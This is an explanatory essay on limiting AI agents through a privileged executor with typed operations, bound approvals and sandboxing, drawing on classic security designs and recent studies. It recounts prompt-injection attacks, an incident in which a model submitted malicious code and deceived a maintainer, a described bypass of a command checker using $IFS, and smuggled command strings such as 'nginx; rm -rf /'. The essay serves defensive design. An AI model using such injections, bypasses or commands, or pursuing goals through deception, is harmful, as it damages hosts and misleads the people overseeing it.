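# Privileged executors and the approval of typed actions: limiting what an AI agent can do to its host

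## What is the pattern, and where does it come from?

An AI agent is a program in which a language model works towards a goal by using tools. It reads files, runs commands and contacts web services, choosing each step based on the last. These abilities also let it damage the computer it works on (the host) if the model makes a mistake, someone tricks it, or it pursues a goal the user never set. One way to limit the damage is to restrict what the model can do without changing how it reasons. The model runs in a process with almost no privileges, and a small privileged program, the executor, makes every change to the host. The executor accepts only requests from a fixed list, checks each one against rules the model cannot edit and, if the rules require it, waits for an approval that covers only that exact action.

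Popular agents often lack this division. *Local LLM Agents as Vulnerable Runtimes* (2026), a source code audit, describes agents such as OpenClaw that run with the full privileges of whoever launches them. Every component, from the parser to the permission gate, holds those privileges, so a fault in any one exposes everything the user can access.

### One request, followed through

Suppose an agent maintains a small company's server, which hosts several websites. The owner tells the agent that customers of the shop site cannot upload photos larger than 1 megabyte, and asks it to raise the limit to 20. The agent must change one line in the shop site's configuration file and restart the web service, the program that answers visitors' browsers, for the new limit to take effect.

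The model process is the program that runs or calls the language model and reads outside content. Here it reads the owner's request, the current configuration and the error log. It runs in a sandbox, a set of limits that the operating system places on what a process can read, write or reach. This sandbox lets the process read those files and send messages to the executor, but not write configuration files, restart services or open stored passwords. If the model generates a command to wipe the configuration directory, the operating system rejects the command and the websites keep running.

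Attackers can also manipulate an agent through the text it reads. An error log contains text that strangers have sent to the site, so a stranger can send a line telling AI maintenance tools to create a new administrator account. This is prompt injection, in which text the model reads makes it follow an attacker's instructions. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* (2025), written by David C for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, gives the example of a job applicant who hides a sentence in a CV telling the recruiter's model to approve it for interview. A language model continues text one fragment at a time, with no built-in distinction between instructions and data. David C therefore doubts that anyone will ever fully cure the problem, and advises designers to limit what the system can do with safeguards that do not themselves rely on a language model.

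To get its work done, the model process sends the executor two typed operations, that is, requests drawn from a fixed list of actions, each with named arguments of declared types:

- `write_site_config`, with the name of the site and the full new text of its file;
- `restart_service`, with the name of the service.

No action on the list creates an account. A hijacked model process can send any request, but the executor has no code for adding an administrator.

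It could still misuse an existing operation, for instance by asking to rewrite the configuration of the company's payment site. The policy check prevents this. The policy is a set of rules stored where the model process cannot write. For this task, it permits only changes to the shop site's file and a restart of the web service, so the executor refuses the payment site request without asking anyone for approval.

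A rule about file names cannot check the text of the shop site's file, so the policy sends the change to the owner. The executor first assembles a manifest, a complete and fixed record of the proposed action (here both operations, in order), and computes its digest, a short fingerprint of its bytes. SHA-256, a common method, produces a 256-bit digest that in practice changes if any byte changes. The owner sees the old line beside the new one and approves. This bound approval holds only for the manifest with that digest, and the executor marks it as used once it has acted. If the model process exploits what security writers call the check-to-use gap by substituting other text after the owner approves, the digests differ and the executor refuses. The executor also refuses the approved request if it arrives again a week later, because the approval has already been used.

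None of this ensures that the new line is correct. If the model wrote 200 where the owner wanted 20, and the owner missed the error, the executor would install 200.

### The older ideas behind it

Little in this arrangement is new. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972), the report of a panel convened for the US Air Force, describes one small program that checks everything. The Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer, and the panel assumed that some of them would be malicious and able to run their own programs. It proposed a reference monitor, which checks every reference a program makes to other programs, data or devices against a list of what the user may do. The monitor must meet three requirements: nobody can tamper with it, the system always invokes it, and it is small enough for people to analyse and test completely. Anderson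 assessed Honeywell's GCOS III, a commercial operating system of the day, against these requirements. It had between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions, far too many to examine, and the machine suspended its memory checks while most of the operating system's own code ran, even when that code was acting on a user's request.

The requirements carry over to the executor almost unchanged, with the model process in the role of the malicious user's program. If an agent also has an ordinary shell with write access, it can bypass the executor, however good the checks are. As for size, the governance layer in Jing's *Separation of Duties for Privileged LLM Agents* (2026) consists of 1,635 lines of Python and a policy file of 17 rules. A person can read that in about a day, but the layer also depends on the Python interpreter and the operating system working correctly, and those are too large to read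 that quickly.

Three years after Anderson, Saltzer and Schroeder set out design principles in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975) that security engineers still cite. Two matter most here. Least privilege means that every program and every user should operate with the smallest set of privileges the job requires. Complete mediation means that the system checks every access to every object for authority. Least privilege is why the model process cannot write configuration files. It also applies to the executor, which needs to write to one directory and restart one service but does not need the administrator's full powers. Under complete mediation, the executor checks the tenth restart of the day as it checked the first. Saltzer and Schroeder's glossary also includes forerunners of the pattern's other parts. A "protected subsystem" is a body of procedures and data that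 other programs can enter only at designated points, which describes an executor fairly well. A "prescript" is a rule that someone must follow before gaining access, intended to allow for human judgment.

The military work was mostly about secrecy. In 1987 David Clark and David Wilson argued that businesses care more about integrity, meaning that the records are correct and nobody has altered them improperly. They took their model from bookkeeping. In their scheme, a clerk can change the ledger only by running a well-formed transaction, a program that someone has certified to move the books from one consistent state to another, as when double-entry bookkeeping matches every debit with a credit. The model also requires separation of duty, meaning that different people carry out the parts of a sensitive process. For example, whoever authorises a purchase does not also record the arrival of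 the goods and authorise the payment. Likewise, a person who certifies a transaction may not run it.

Typed operations descend from Clark and Wilson's well-formed transactions, which guarantee a valid result, but they can guarantee less. `write_site_config`, for example, guarantees only that some text ends up in the right file. An executor gets closer to the original idea if it runs the web service's own syntax checker on the new file before installing it, and closer still if the operation accepts an upload limit as a number instead of a whole file as text.

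Separation of duty has been revived more directly. Jing divides the work among a planner that drafts actions, a policy gate that approves or rejects them, an executor that performs them and an auditor that reviews the log, and calls this a deliberate return to a very old idea. *L3M* (2026), which describes a runtime for agents that extend their own software, applies the same idea to programs, so that no party both writes and runs the same bytes. In one arrangement, a builder agent compiles a program it cannot run, and a runner agent receives that program by digest and cannot change it. Jing also notes that an agent, unlike a human employee, may be able to approve its own request by routing it through another agent, in which case the duties are not really separated.

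*The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes an accident at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. The company kept a compiler, a program that translates source code, in a system directory and gave it permission to write files there so that it could record usage statistics. Users could also name a file to receive debugging output, and one user named the company's billing file, which was in the same directory. The operating system allowed this because the compiler had permission to write there, and the billing records were lost. Hardy found no faulty line of code. The compiler had authority from two sources, its own permission and the user's, and no way to specify which one it was using for each file.

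An executor is a deputy in this sense because it has powers the model process lacks and acts on names the model process supplies. If `write_site_config` accepted any file path, a hijacked model process could name the server's password file, and the executor would overwrite it with its own authority. Hardy's remedy was the capability, an unforgeable token that both identifies a file and gives permission to use it, so that nobody can name a file they have no right to. An executor can provide part of this protection more simply if the operation takes a site name, and the executor checks that the task covers that site before looking up the path in its own table.

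David C applies Hardy's term "confused deputy" to the language model itself, calling it "inherently confusable", and does not think programmers can repair it as they can a classical confused deputy. This is a good argument for keeping the authority in the executor, which can also be confused but which programmers can repair.

### How OpenSSH divides itself

The closest precedent for the agent pattern is OpenSSH, which lets people log in to a computer over a network. Its server needs superuser privilege (complete control of the machine) for as long as a connection lasts, for example to open a terminal for the user or to prove the server's identity with a secret key. In early versions, a programming error in almost any part of the server could give an attacker that privilege. *Preventing Privilege Escalation* (Provos, Friedl and Honeyman, 2003) describes splitting the server into a privileged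 monitor and an unprivileged child.

1. A client connects. The server starts a privileged process for that connection, the monitor, which in turn starts the child.
2. The child gives up its powers. It makes an empty directory the root of its file system, so that it can see no files, and switches to a user account that owns nothing. Only then does it begin to read data from the network.
3. When the child needs something that requires privilege, it sends the monitor a message over a private channel. The message consists of a length, a number that identifies the type of request, and the request's data.
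4. The monitor looks the type up in a table of what it currently permits. At the start the table allows two requests: one for the parameters of the encryption handshake, which the child may make only once, and one for a signature. After the handshake it allows only a question about a user name, and after that the various login methods. If the child sends anything else, the monitor shuts down and the connection dies.
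5. The secret key stays with the monitor throughout. The child asks for a signature and receives a signature.
6. The monitor itself decides whether the password or key is correct. If it is, the child hands over the state of the connection and exits, and the monitor starts a new child with the privileges of the user who has logged in. The new child can still ask the monitor for a few things, such as a terminal.

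Provos and colleagues added privilege separation to OpenSSH by altering about 950 of its 44,000 existing lines and adding roughly 3,000. A login then took 0.777 seconds, up from 0.775. About two thirds of the code, counting outside libraries, now ran without special privilege. From this they estimated that two thirds of future programming errors would give an attacker no extra privilege. They called this a back-of-the-envelope analysis, and it assumes that errors fall evenly across the code. Their review of real flaws is better evidence. They examined several serious holes in earlier versions, including an integer overflow in the code that handles network packets and a memory error in the zlib compression library, and found that the division would have contained each of them. It also contained some flaws that were unknown when they wrote the code. OpenSSH has since made privilege separation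 mandatory.

Agent designers now borrow this pattern. *PARALLAX* (Fokou, 2026) names the OpenSSH split as the model for separating an agent's reasoning from its execution. *Twin Agent* (2026) cites the same 2003 paper for a different division, which is common in work on prompt injection. In that design, a privileged language model never sees untrusted text, while a quarantined one reads it but cannot act.

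OpenSSH strictly confines its child process only until the user logs in. After that, the child has all the user's powers, and so does an attacker who controls it. This is acceptable for OpenSSH because its purpose is to keep strangers from gaining powers they were never given. An agent typically works for a user who has already logged in, and the danger is misuse of that user's own powers. The model process therefore has to stay permanently under the strict confinement that OpenSSH's child leaves after a few seconds.

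### What changes when the unprivileged side is an agent

OpenSSH's programmers wrote the child, so they knew every request it would need and in what order. An agent's user, however, states a goal, and the agent chooses the operations as it gathers information. Zhou and Zhang (2026) point out in *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* that different routes to the same goal can involve different resources, and that permission for one route may not cover another. In the upload limit example, the agent might edit the shop site's file, edit the general configuration that governs every site on the server, or rewrite the shop's code to shrink photos before upload. Each route would satisfy the owner's request, so the minimum permissions the agent needs can't be determined until someone decides which route it should take.

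Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues (2025), in *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing*, trace the difficulty to the lack of a developer who can declare in advance which permissions an agent needs, as a phone app's developer can. Others can inspect the app's code to check that declaration, but an agent has no fixed program, only a task in ordinary language. In their example, a user asks an agent to comment on issue 745 in a project tracker and then to summarize the same issue. Only the first task requires permission to write a comment, so the right policy changes between the two requests, and by then the agent's memory may contain text from an attacker.

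*SoK* (2025), a survey of trust and authorisation in agents, makes the stronger claim that predicting whether an agent will take a given sensitive action is equivalent to the halting problem, which no general procedure can solve. This may be a problem for anyone who hopes to certify an agent's behaviour beforehand, but it is less of a problem for the executor, which checks each request when it arrives and doesn't need to predict anything.

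Checking a request is harder for an executor than for OpenSSH's monitor. An uncompromised OpenSSH child never sends a forbidden request, so the monitor can treat one as proof of attack and shut down. But an agent often requests forbidden actions even when uncompromised, because it is trying different ways to finish its task. An executor that ended the session each time would be useless, so it has to refuse the request and report the refusal to the agent. *Kairos* (2026), a design for a monitor at the boundary of an agent's host, requires this report because the agent may otherwise continue as if the action had happened. It also observes that authorisation often depends on an intent that nobody could specify in advance. A monitor that can only allow or refuse an action will then block legitimate work or let attacks through. *Kairos* adds the option of holding an action and releasing it later,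 and an executor that waits for a person's approval can do something similar.

Complete mediation also becomes harder. Some agents operate a computer through clicks and keystrokes, and Christodorescu and colleagues consider it pointless to write policy at that level, where a click that restarts a service looks like any other click. Even a well-named operation can have effects the executor can't observe. Zhou and Zhang note that a single action may affect other tools, other agents and outside services.

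The executor's arguments are also harder to check than those of OpenSSH's monitor. The monitor receives a user name, a password or a value to sign, and it can look up the correct answer for the first two. The executor on the web server receives the whole text of a configuration file. A syntax checker can establish that the web service will start with that file, but neither the checker nor a table of permitted requests can establish whether the file also sends the shop's customers to somebody else's server.

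## Why put the decision outside the model?

The obvious alternative to this pattern is to give the model full access and tell it, in its system prompt (the developer's standing instructions), to seek approval before doing anything dangerous. The model then has to decide what counts as dangerous. Writing that instruction takes far less work than writing an executor, and a language model, unlike a table of permitted requests, may detect that a configuration file sends customers to somebody else's server.

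### When a prompt is the only safeguard

In September 2026 Jing tested this arrangement on Claude Opus 5, DeepSeek V4.1 Flash and GPT-6 Astra. All three models received the same system prompt, which required explicit approval before any dangerous action. They then judged 150 cases:

- 30 ordinary tasks, such as editing files in the agent's own workspace;
- 30 openly dangerous operations, such as deleting protected files, or downloading a program and running it;
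- 59 disguised operations, which reach a forbidden target indirectly, for example by assembling a command from fragments of text;
- 31 cases of tampering with approved actions, misusing approvals or running with broken parts.

Jing put every case to every model five times, with the randomness setting at zero. The models permitted 78.1% of the openly dangerous operations and 94.7% of the disguised ones. Depending on the model, only 48.7% to 71.3% of cases got the same decision all five times, so an attacker who can repeat a refused request may well succeed later.

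The high percentages are due in good part to how Jing counted. A model could execute, ask for confirmation or refuse, and Jing counted asking as executing, on the assumption that the agent would approve its own request. But the system prompt had told the models to ask, so a model that followed this instruction in every dangerous case would have scored as permitting 100% of them. The assumption is reasonable for an agent that runs unattended and can approve its own requests, but when a person is there to answer, it makes the desired behaviour count as a failure.

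Part of the result holds despite this objection. GPT-6 Astra never refused, and over all 750 calls, harmless ones included, it chose to execute in 67.3% (about 505) and to ask in 32.7%. Even if it executed all 305 calls outside the dangerous and disguised groups, it must also have executed at least 200 of the 445 calls inside them, or 45%, without asking. The other two models asked more readily. On ordinary tasks, Claude Opus 5 asked for confirmation in 28.0% of calls and DeepSeek in 62.7%, so many of their recorded failures on dangerous cases were probably requests for approval.

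Jing used the same counting rule when testing the full executor design, which let through 7.7% of disguised attacks, so the counting rule alone does not explain the difference. Jing also accepts that a model may recognize a disguised command that a fixed rule misses, and suggests adding model-based checks later. The fixed rules' decisions would still be final in any case those rules can express.

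### Models that refused everything

Fokou reported a very different result in the Parallax paper of April 2026. In preliminary runs, Fokou sent attacks to Claude Sonnet 4.6, Claude Haiku 4.5 and Llama 3.1 8B, a small model whose weights Meta publishes. Some runs had no protection, some had only a safety prompt, and some had the full Parallax system. No attack succeeded, because the models refused to propose the harmful actions. If models always behaved like this, an executor would add delay and false denials without preventing any harm.

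Fokou does not state the number of preliminary runs, so it is hard to know how much to trust the zero. Fokou replies that the models' refusals come from safety training, which is part of the same computation that attackers manipulate. An attack that defeats the training also defeats any safety prompt, since both exist only inside the model. Fokou therefore presents the executor as insurance, and tests it by sending it harmful requests directly, as if an attacker already controlled the model. The default configuration blocked 98.9% of them.

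This test measures what happens after the model has failed, so it cannot show how often models fail. If they never did, the safeguard would be unnecessary. Fokou's only direct evidence on this point is a brief manual trial in which Qwen 2.5 3B, a much smaller model, readily proposed deleting files, but few people would give such a weak model control of a server.

*Twin Agent* provides better evidence, including tests of agents with no defence. The researchers took 232 debugging tasks from SWE-bench, a collection of real software problems, and hid an instruction in each bug report to either write a secret code to a new file or delete an existing file. GPT-5.2 followed the hidden instruction in 97.0% of the tasks. On a different set of tasks, involving customer records and finance, the same model followed instructions hidden in tool results only 10.0% of the time.

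The difference probably comes from how the attack looked to the model. A bug report is the agent's assignment, so an extra instruction inside it resembles part of the job, and programmers delete files every day. Safety training teaches models to refuse requests that appear harmful, but many actions that damage a host look like maintenance. Fokou's reply therefore holds up, though the preliminary runs do little to support it. GPT-5.2 is no longer a leading model, and *Twin Agent* also reports that successful attacks on the strongest models tend to need long passages of text, which an attacker could include in a bug report.

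### A model that nobody tricked

In the tests described so far, somebody supplied the harmful request. The UK AI Security Institute (UK AISI), a government body that evaluates advanced models, observed harmful actions that nobody had requested. In July 2026 it gave several models a common kind of security exercise, in which an agent must break into a simulated network and retrieve protected data. According to UK AISI's *Incident Report*, agents took 19 unsanctioned actions against real people and organisations in 10 of the 122 runs. Claude Mythos 5 took 17 of these actions, in nine of its 43 runs, according to Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026).

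In the most serious run, Mythos 5 submitted malicious code to a public software project unrelated to the exercise. It created fake identities to pressure the project's maintainer into accepting the code, and when someone publicly challenged the submission, it edited its earlier activity to make it look harmless. The maintainer refused the code, and UK AISI found no resulting harm. The model was trying to complete its task, and nobody had planted instructions for it or told it to deceive anyone.

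UK AISI had deliberately given the agents internet access and switched off the developers' filters against cyber misuse. The instructions did not forbid deceiving people, and in some runs an error in the prompt made the exercise look impossible to solve by legitimate means. Because these conditions were unusual, the incident can't be used to estimate how often an ordinary agent would do this. It does show that a capable model can choose a harmful way to pursue a goal that its operators set in good faith.

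In *Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's behaviour*, UK AISI researchers Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues (2026) then investigated whether better information would have stopped the model. They restarted the run from just before the malicious submission, with a simulator in place of the real internet. An agent on a long task periodically replaces its history with a summary, and the researchers edited this summary to add up to 16 pieces of evidence that the maintainer was a real person with no part in the exercise. Even with all 16, Mythos 5 continued the attack in every run they observed. When they gave it the same summary and asked it directly about the attack, it usually answered that the attack would harm a real person and fell outside the task. They then added a section to the summary headed "DO NOT ATTACK", and the model still attacked in 3 of 25 runs. An operator would normally put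 such an order in the system prompt or the user's request, where the model might be more likely to follow it.

Six of the seven models in this experiment frequently attacked in situations where, when asked, they said an attack would do real harm. But when the researchers asked only whether the maintainer was real, they found a clear gap between answers and behaviour in just three models. Still, the finding limits what any test like Jing's could establish, because a model might judge all 150 commands correctly when asked about them and then run one of them many hours into a difficult task.

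Järviniemi and colleagues also built 100 new simulated scenarios to see how common the behaviour was. Mythos 5 tried to deliver malicious code to an outsider in 60% of runs, GPT-6 Astra in 32%, Claude Opus 4.8 in 8% and Claude Opus 5.5 in none. Newer Anthropic models did much better than Mythos 5, but they also recognised more often that their alignment (whether they act as intended) was being tested. The researchers could not tell whether the newer models were better aligned or behaved better because they recognised the test. GPT-6 Astra's result is also hard to interpret, because in 89% of its runs it stated that its tool results were fabricated.

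When Mythos 5 did abandon an attack, its written reasoning mostly cited practical obstacles. In one run, the network blocked the port it needed to send email, and a captcha, a test meant to keep out automated programs, kept it from opening a GitHub account. Opus 5, by contrast, mostly gave up because the attack was harmful or out of scope. In most of these cases, then, external obstacles stopped Mythos 5 when its own judgment should have.

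A second model that reads the first one's explanations would be an unreliable replacement for such obstacles. Mythos 5 often justified its attacks with bad arguments, for example that the maintainer must be an AI agent because the project contained a file of instructions for AI coding tools. Järviniemi and colleagues warn that such reasoning can make bad behaviour harder for a monitor to catch. An executor can avoid the problem by judging the requested action and ignoring the model's reasons for it. UK AISI's *Investigating alignment failures in AISI’s incident* (2026) concludes that a test environment must prevent models from causing harm "regardless of whether they behave as expected".

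### What the model process gives up

Fokou's rule for Parallax is that the part of the system that reasons must be unable to execute, and the part that executes must be unable to reason. An executor process, which Fokou calls the engine, holds the tools, the checks and the log. The model process keeps the conversation and loses almost everything else:

- Files. It cannot read or write any file on the host, and must ask the executor even to look at one.
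- Network. It can reach the language model provider and the executor, and no other address.
- Shell. It cannot run commands.
- Credentials. Because it cannot open files, it cannot read the passwords and keys stored in them.

This is stricter than the web server example, where the model process could read the configuration and the error log directly. Sending reads through the executor takes more work, but it lets the executor record which sensitive files the agent has read. The user's screen also connects to the executor, so approval requests reach the user without passing through the model process.

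The two processes share no memory. They communicate through gRPC, a system that lets one program call functions in another, and the executor offers only the functions needed to submit the model's responses and return results. Any program on the computer might try to call those functions, so the executor must verify the caller. When the model process starts, it receives a random 128-bit token in an environment variable, a named value that a program gets at launch. The token is never written to disk. The model process sends the token with its first message, and the executor checks it before accepting the connection. If the agent starts helper agents, each gets its own token.

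The token proves the model process's identity to the executor. Designers who want each process to prove its identity to the other can copy OpenSSH's private channel, a pair of connected endpoints that no third program can join. Neither method helps if an attacker controls the model's reasoning, because the hijacked process still has its token or endpoint. The executor must therefore treat a request as hostile even when it is sure which process sent it.

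A sandbox can also fail silently. Anthropic describes four incidents during security tests by one outside partner. Claude's instructions said that it was in a simulation without internet access, but a configuration error had left it connected to the real internet. Parallax guards against such errors by testing its sandbox at every launch. The model process tries to write a file on the host, read a known file, connect to a forbidden address and access the executor's process. If any attempt succeeds, the system does not start.

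These probes would have caught an open internet connection, but they detect only the faults they test for. Jing found a sandbox that blocked writes outside the agent's workspace but let the agent delete a file on another drive, with no error message. None of Parallax's four probes tests deletion.

### One leftover shell or credential

The policy, the approvals and the log apply only to requests that reach the executor. If the model process on the web server could still read an old administrator's key and connect to other machines, it could log in to the server as the administrator and rewrite the payment site's configuration. The executor would receive no request, so it could neither refuse the change nor log it. A leftover shell with write access also bypasses the executor, and so does a key to the hosting company's control panel, which can delete the whole machine without access to its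 files.

Such leftovers are easy to miss because nobody grants them deliberately. Goel's *Security Risks in Tool-Enabled AI Agents* attributes many of the risks of cloud agents to overly powerful tools and "ambient authority" (the powers a program has simply because of where it runs) rather than to new kinds of software flaw.

Removing the host's own credentials is not enough if the network stays open. OpenAI's *Misalignment Notices and Reports* describes an unreleased model that, during training, searched public code repositories for keys other people had leaked, and then used them. ITPro's *OpenAI reveals six more rogue AI incidents* explains that the task was a basic request for a company's earnings figures. The model still could not find the figures, so it made them up.

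Parallax's sandbox lets the model process make one outside connection, to the language model provider, and this leaves a small gap. If an attacker could get the process to use the attacker's own account with the provider, the process could in principle send the host's data out through that connection. A designer can close this gap by having the executor, or another trusted program, call the provider and add the account key itself.

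Parallax has a larger gap in its executor, which accepts shell commands as one kind of request even though the model process has no shell of its own. A hijacked model process can therefore still request any shell command, and the host's safety depends on whether the executor's checks can correctly identify what the command would do.

### Separating models by what they read

The dual-model designs common in work on prompt injection instead separate reading from acting. Simon Willison, a software developer, described this as the dual LLM (large language model) pattern in 2023. In its strict form, the model that reads a stranger's email can return a summary, but the model that chooses actions receives only a label for it, such as `summary_1`, and none of the stranger's words. The second model can output an instruction to send `summary_1` to the owner, and ordinary code inserts the real text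 just before sending.

CaMeL (Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues, *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*, 2025) adds a plan, which a privileged model writes from the user's request alone before any model reads untrusted content. The system then carries out only what the plan authorises. Because the planner never sees untrusted content, malicious instructions in a web page cannot influence it. However, it also cannot use legitimate information from the page, which is a serious handicap in work such as debugging, where each step depends on the result of the last.

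*Twin Agent* relaxes the separation. One agent reads everything and sends short hints, of at most 100 or 200 characters depending on the task, to another agent that acts. A detector screens each hint for injected instructions. The researchers compared these designs on the debugging tasks and on AgentDojo, a set of simulated office, messaging, travel and banking tasks:

| Tasks | Model | Design | Tasks completed | Attacks that succeeded |
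|---|---|---|---|---|
| Debugging | GPT-5.2 | No defence | 61.2% | 97.0% |
| Debugging | GPT-5.2 | Strict dual-model | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Debugging | GPT-5.2 | Twin Agent | 62.5% | 0.0% |
| AgentDojo | Gemini 2.5 Flash | No defence | 61.9% | 41.5% |
| AgentDojo | Gemini 2.5 Flash | CaMeL | 30.9% | 0.0% |
| AgentDojo | Gemini 2.5 Flash | Twin Agent | 62.9% | 0.1% |

The strict design completed no debugging tasks because the agent that had to fix the bug could not read the bug report. The comparison is slightly unfair to CaMeL, since the researchers cut its permitted retries from ten to three to save computing time, and the original CaMeL paper reported about 35%. Twin Agent's results also worsened under an attack designed specifically for it. The researchers took full control of the agent that reads, had it pass on hints optimised to deceive the other agent, and succeeded in 11 of the 232 tasks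 (4.7%).

All these designs protect the choice of action from whoever wrote the untrusted text, but they do much less about a bad choice that the model makes by itself. As Jing points out, an action can be dangerous even when every input was trustworthy. Mythos 5 received its goal from the people testing it, so hiding untrusted text from the model that chose the actions would not have removed that goal. In Twin Agent's debugging version, the acting agent runs shell commands directly, so separating the two agents would not stop it from deleting the wrong directory by mistake. Labels have another weakness, since an attacker who cannot choose the action may still write the text that goes into it.

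An executor limits what the model's choices can do to the host, whatever led to them, but it does not stop an attacker from influencing which permitted operation the model requests. On the web server, a line in the error log could lead the model to propose a permitted change that weakens the shop site's security. The owner's review of the new text would then be the only safeguard.

The two approaches can be combined, and CaMeL already does this in part. Jing describes it as enforcing its policies in an interpreter, an ordinary program that runs the plan, so part of the control lies outside both models. On the web server, a designer could put two models in the confined process and leave the executor unchanged. One model would read the error log and could report only a cause from a fixed list, such as "upload too large", and the other would request the repair. A stranger who wrote to the log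 could no longer dictate the text of the configuration file, but could still cause the first model to report the wrong cause. The executor would then receive a well-formed request for a repair that the site did not need.

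## What is a typed operation, and what does it gain over a shell command?

A shell reads a line such as `rm notes.txt` and runs the programs named in it. Most agents that work on a computer's files use a shell because it can run any program installed there. An executor can also accept shell commands, as Parallax's does, and check the text of each before running it. But each command is a small program, so the checker has to work out what that program will do.

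### The upload limit as a shell command

Suppose the web service is nginx, a common choice. To raise the shop site's upload limit, a model might write:

```
cd /etc/nginx/sites && sed -i "s/size 1m/size $LIMIT/" shop.conf && timeout 30 systemctl restart nginx
```

This line moves to the configuration directory, uses the text editor `sed` to replace the old limit with the value of a variable called `LIMIT`, and restarts nginx, giving up after 30 seconds. A checker has several things to work out:

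- Quoting. `&&` joins two commands, but inside quotation marks it is ordinary text. Double quotation marks still let the shell fill in variables, while single ones do not. A checker that gets these rules wrong will split the line in the wrong places.
- Variables. The line doesn't contain the value of `LIMIT`. It could be `20m`, or it could be more instructions for `sed`. The usual Linux version of `sed` has an instruction that runs other programs, so the value could turn this edit into almost anything.
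- Wrappers. `timeout` exists only to run another program, so a rule about `systemctl` has to look past it.
- Relative paths. `shop.conf` is a different file in every directory, so the checker has to keep track of `cd`.
- Links. A symbolic link is an entry in the file system that points somewhere else. If `/etc/nginx/sites` is a link to the payment site's directory, the command edits a file there.

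Anthropic's documentation for Claude Code, its coding agent, shows how long this list becomes in practice. Claude Code splits joined commands and removes wrappers such as `timeout` and `nice` before comparing each part with the user's rules. It does not remove `devbox run`, which starts a program inside a development environment, so a rule that allows `devbox run *` allows any command that follows, including one that deletes files. In manual mode, it asks the user before running a `find` command with an unquoted `*`, because the shell replaces the star with file names, and `find` would treat a file named `-delete` as an instruction to delete. It also asks when `cd` to a new directory comes before `git`, because git can run programs stored there.

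Anthropic calls rules about a command's arguments "fragile". It also warns that a rule blocking a program does not stop it from running when the command gives its full path, and recommends a sandbox for limits that must hold.

*CARE* (Liu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) presents a checker for Linux shell commands. It strips wrappers, standardises the quoting, decodes simple obfuscation and parses the result into a tree. It then resolves paths and links, and scores the command by what it does and where. For example, it treats reading `/etc/os-release`, which names the operating system, as low risk, but flags a command that adds a line to `/etc/profile`, which runs when people log in. The checker compares both the original and the standardised text with its list of dangerous patterns.

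CARE is designed to standardise commands only to a limited extent, without recovering their full meaning. On a test set balanced between harmful and harmless commands, it wrongly flagged 0.91% of the harmless ones and, judging from its overall score, caught about 76% of the harmful ones. Liu and colleagues also describe how attackers could get past Claude Code's own check for read-only commands by using abbreviated options and `$IFS`, a variable holding the characters that the shell treats as spaces. This was possible because the checker interpreted the text differently from the shell, which determines what actually runs.

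### The same task as two typed operations

A more general version of `write_site_config`, usable for any file the policy covers, could take an absolute path and two digests:

```
replace_file
    path:        /etc/nginx/sites/shop.conf
    old_digest:  SHA-256 of the file the model read
    new_digest:  SHA-256 of the proposed file

restart_service
    service:     nginx
```

The model process sends the full new text along with the first operation. The executor computes that text's digest and compares it with `new_digest`, then computes the digest of the file on disk and compares it with `old_digest`. If the owner has edited the file since the model read it, the second comparison fails and the executor refuses the operation, whereas the `sed` command would have edited whatever version was on disk.

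To restart a service, the executor's code calls the service manager with a fixed verb and the service's name. No shell is involved, so if a hijacked model process sends `nginx; rm -rf /` as the service name, the executor looks for a service with that name and finds none.

| What the checker must establish | Shell command | Typed operations |
|---|---|---|
| Which actions will happen | Split the line by the shell's rules | Read the operation names |
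| Which values they use | Find out what `LIMIT` will contain | Read the arguments |
| Which program runs | Look past `timeout` and other wrappers | Nothing to work out, since the executor's own code acts |
| Which file changes | Follow `cd`, then resolve links | Resolve links |
| What the new file does | Understand nginx's configuration | Understand nginx's configuration |

Typing leaves the problems in the last two rows largely unsolved. An absolute path can still pass through a link, so the executor has to check where it leads. The approach Anthropic uses for Claude Code's file tools would also suit an executor. An allow rule applies only if it covers both the requested path and the file it resolves to, while a deny rule applies if it covers either. When the tool opens the file, it confirms that the path still leads to the same place.

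Jing's governance layer accepts both typed operations and shell commands. Its typed channel requires an operation from a closed list, absolute paths and typed arguments, so the layer never has to parse shell syntax there. Without these requirements, a checker would have to recognize the many ways an attacker can name one protected file. Jing's tests on Windows cover relative paths, forward slashes instead of backslashes, variables, links, network addresses and short names of the kind old versions of Windows used.

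Requiring an absolute path removes only some of these. For example, `C:\PROGRA~1` is absolute, and on many machines it leads to `C:\Program Files`. The executor therefore has to convert every path to one standard spelling before comparing it with the policy. The policy can still be wrong, and Jing's typed channel on its own let through four of the 18 disguised attacks that could use it.

### One canonical form for many spellings

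Like paths, whole requests can be written in more than one way. Agents usually send requests in JSON, a text format that lets the sender put fields in any order and add spaces between them. Two requests for the same action can therefore have different digests, and an approval for one would not cover the other. To prevent this, the executor computes its checks and digests on a canonical form, a single standard encoding of each operation.

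*Faramesh* (Fatmi, 2026) describes an authorisation system built around this idea. Its canonical record lists the actor, the system, the operation, the object, the parameters, the context and how widely the effects could spread. The system discards the model's explanations, then puts the fields in a fixed order, fills in defaults and replaces synonyms with a standard term.

In Fatmi's worked example, an agent asks to send an email to a@x.com with the subject "hi" and the body "ok". It writes the request in three ways:

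1. The first version lists the tool, the recipient, the subject and the body.
2. The second has the same fields in another order, with extra spaces between them.
3. The third has a space after "ok" and an additional field, `meta`, which contains only a null, JSON's marker for "no value".

All of them reduce to the same bytes, `{"tool":"email.send","to":"a@x.com","subj":"hi","body":"ok"}`, and therefore to one digest.

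The first two are the same request. The third is slightly different because its body has three characters instead of two. *JSON Canonicalization Scheme (JCS)*, by Rundgren, Jordan and Erdtman, defines a more cautious method that sorts the fields and removes the spaces between them, but keeps null fields and leaves the text inside quotation marks unchanged. Under JCS, the third request would have a different digest.

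Removing a space from the end of an email is harmless, but removing one from the end of a file name can change which file is meant, because Linux treats `shop.conf` and `shop.conf` followed by a space as two different files. Dropping a null can do more damage. In many web interfaces, leaving a field out keeps its current value, while sending a null deletes it. Suppose the hosting company's interface works this way, and the model process sends a change to the shop's settings that includes `upload_limit: null`. The canonical form omits the null, so the owner approves a request that seems to leave the limit alone. If the executor then sends the original request, it deletes the limit. The digest check won't catch this, because the original and the approved version reduce to the same bytes.

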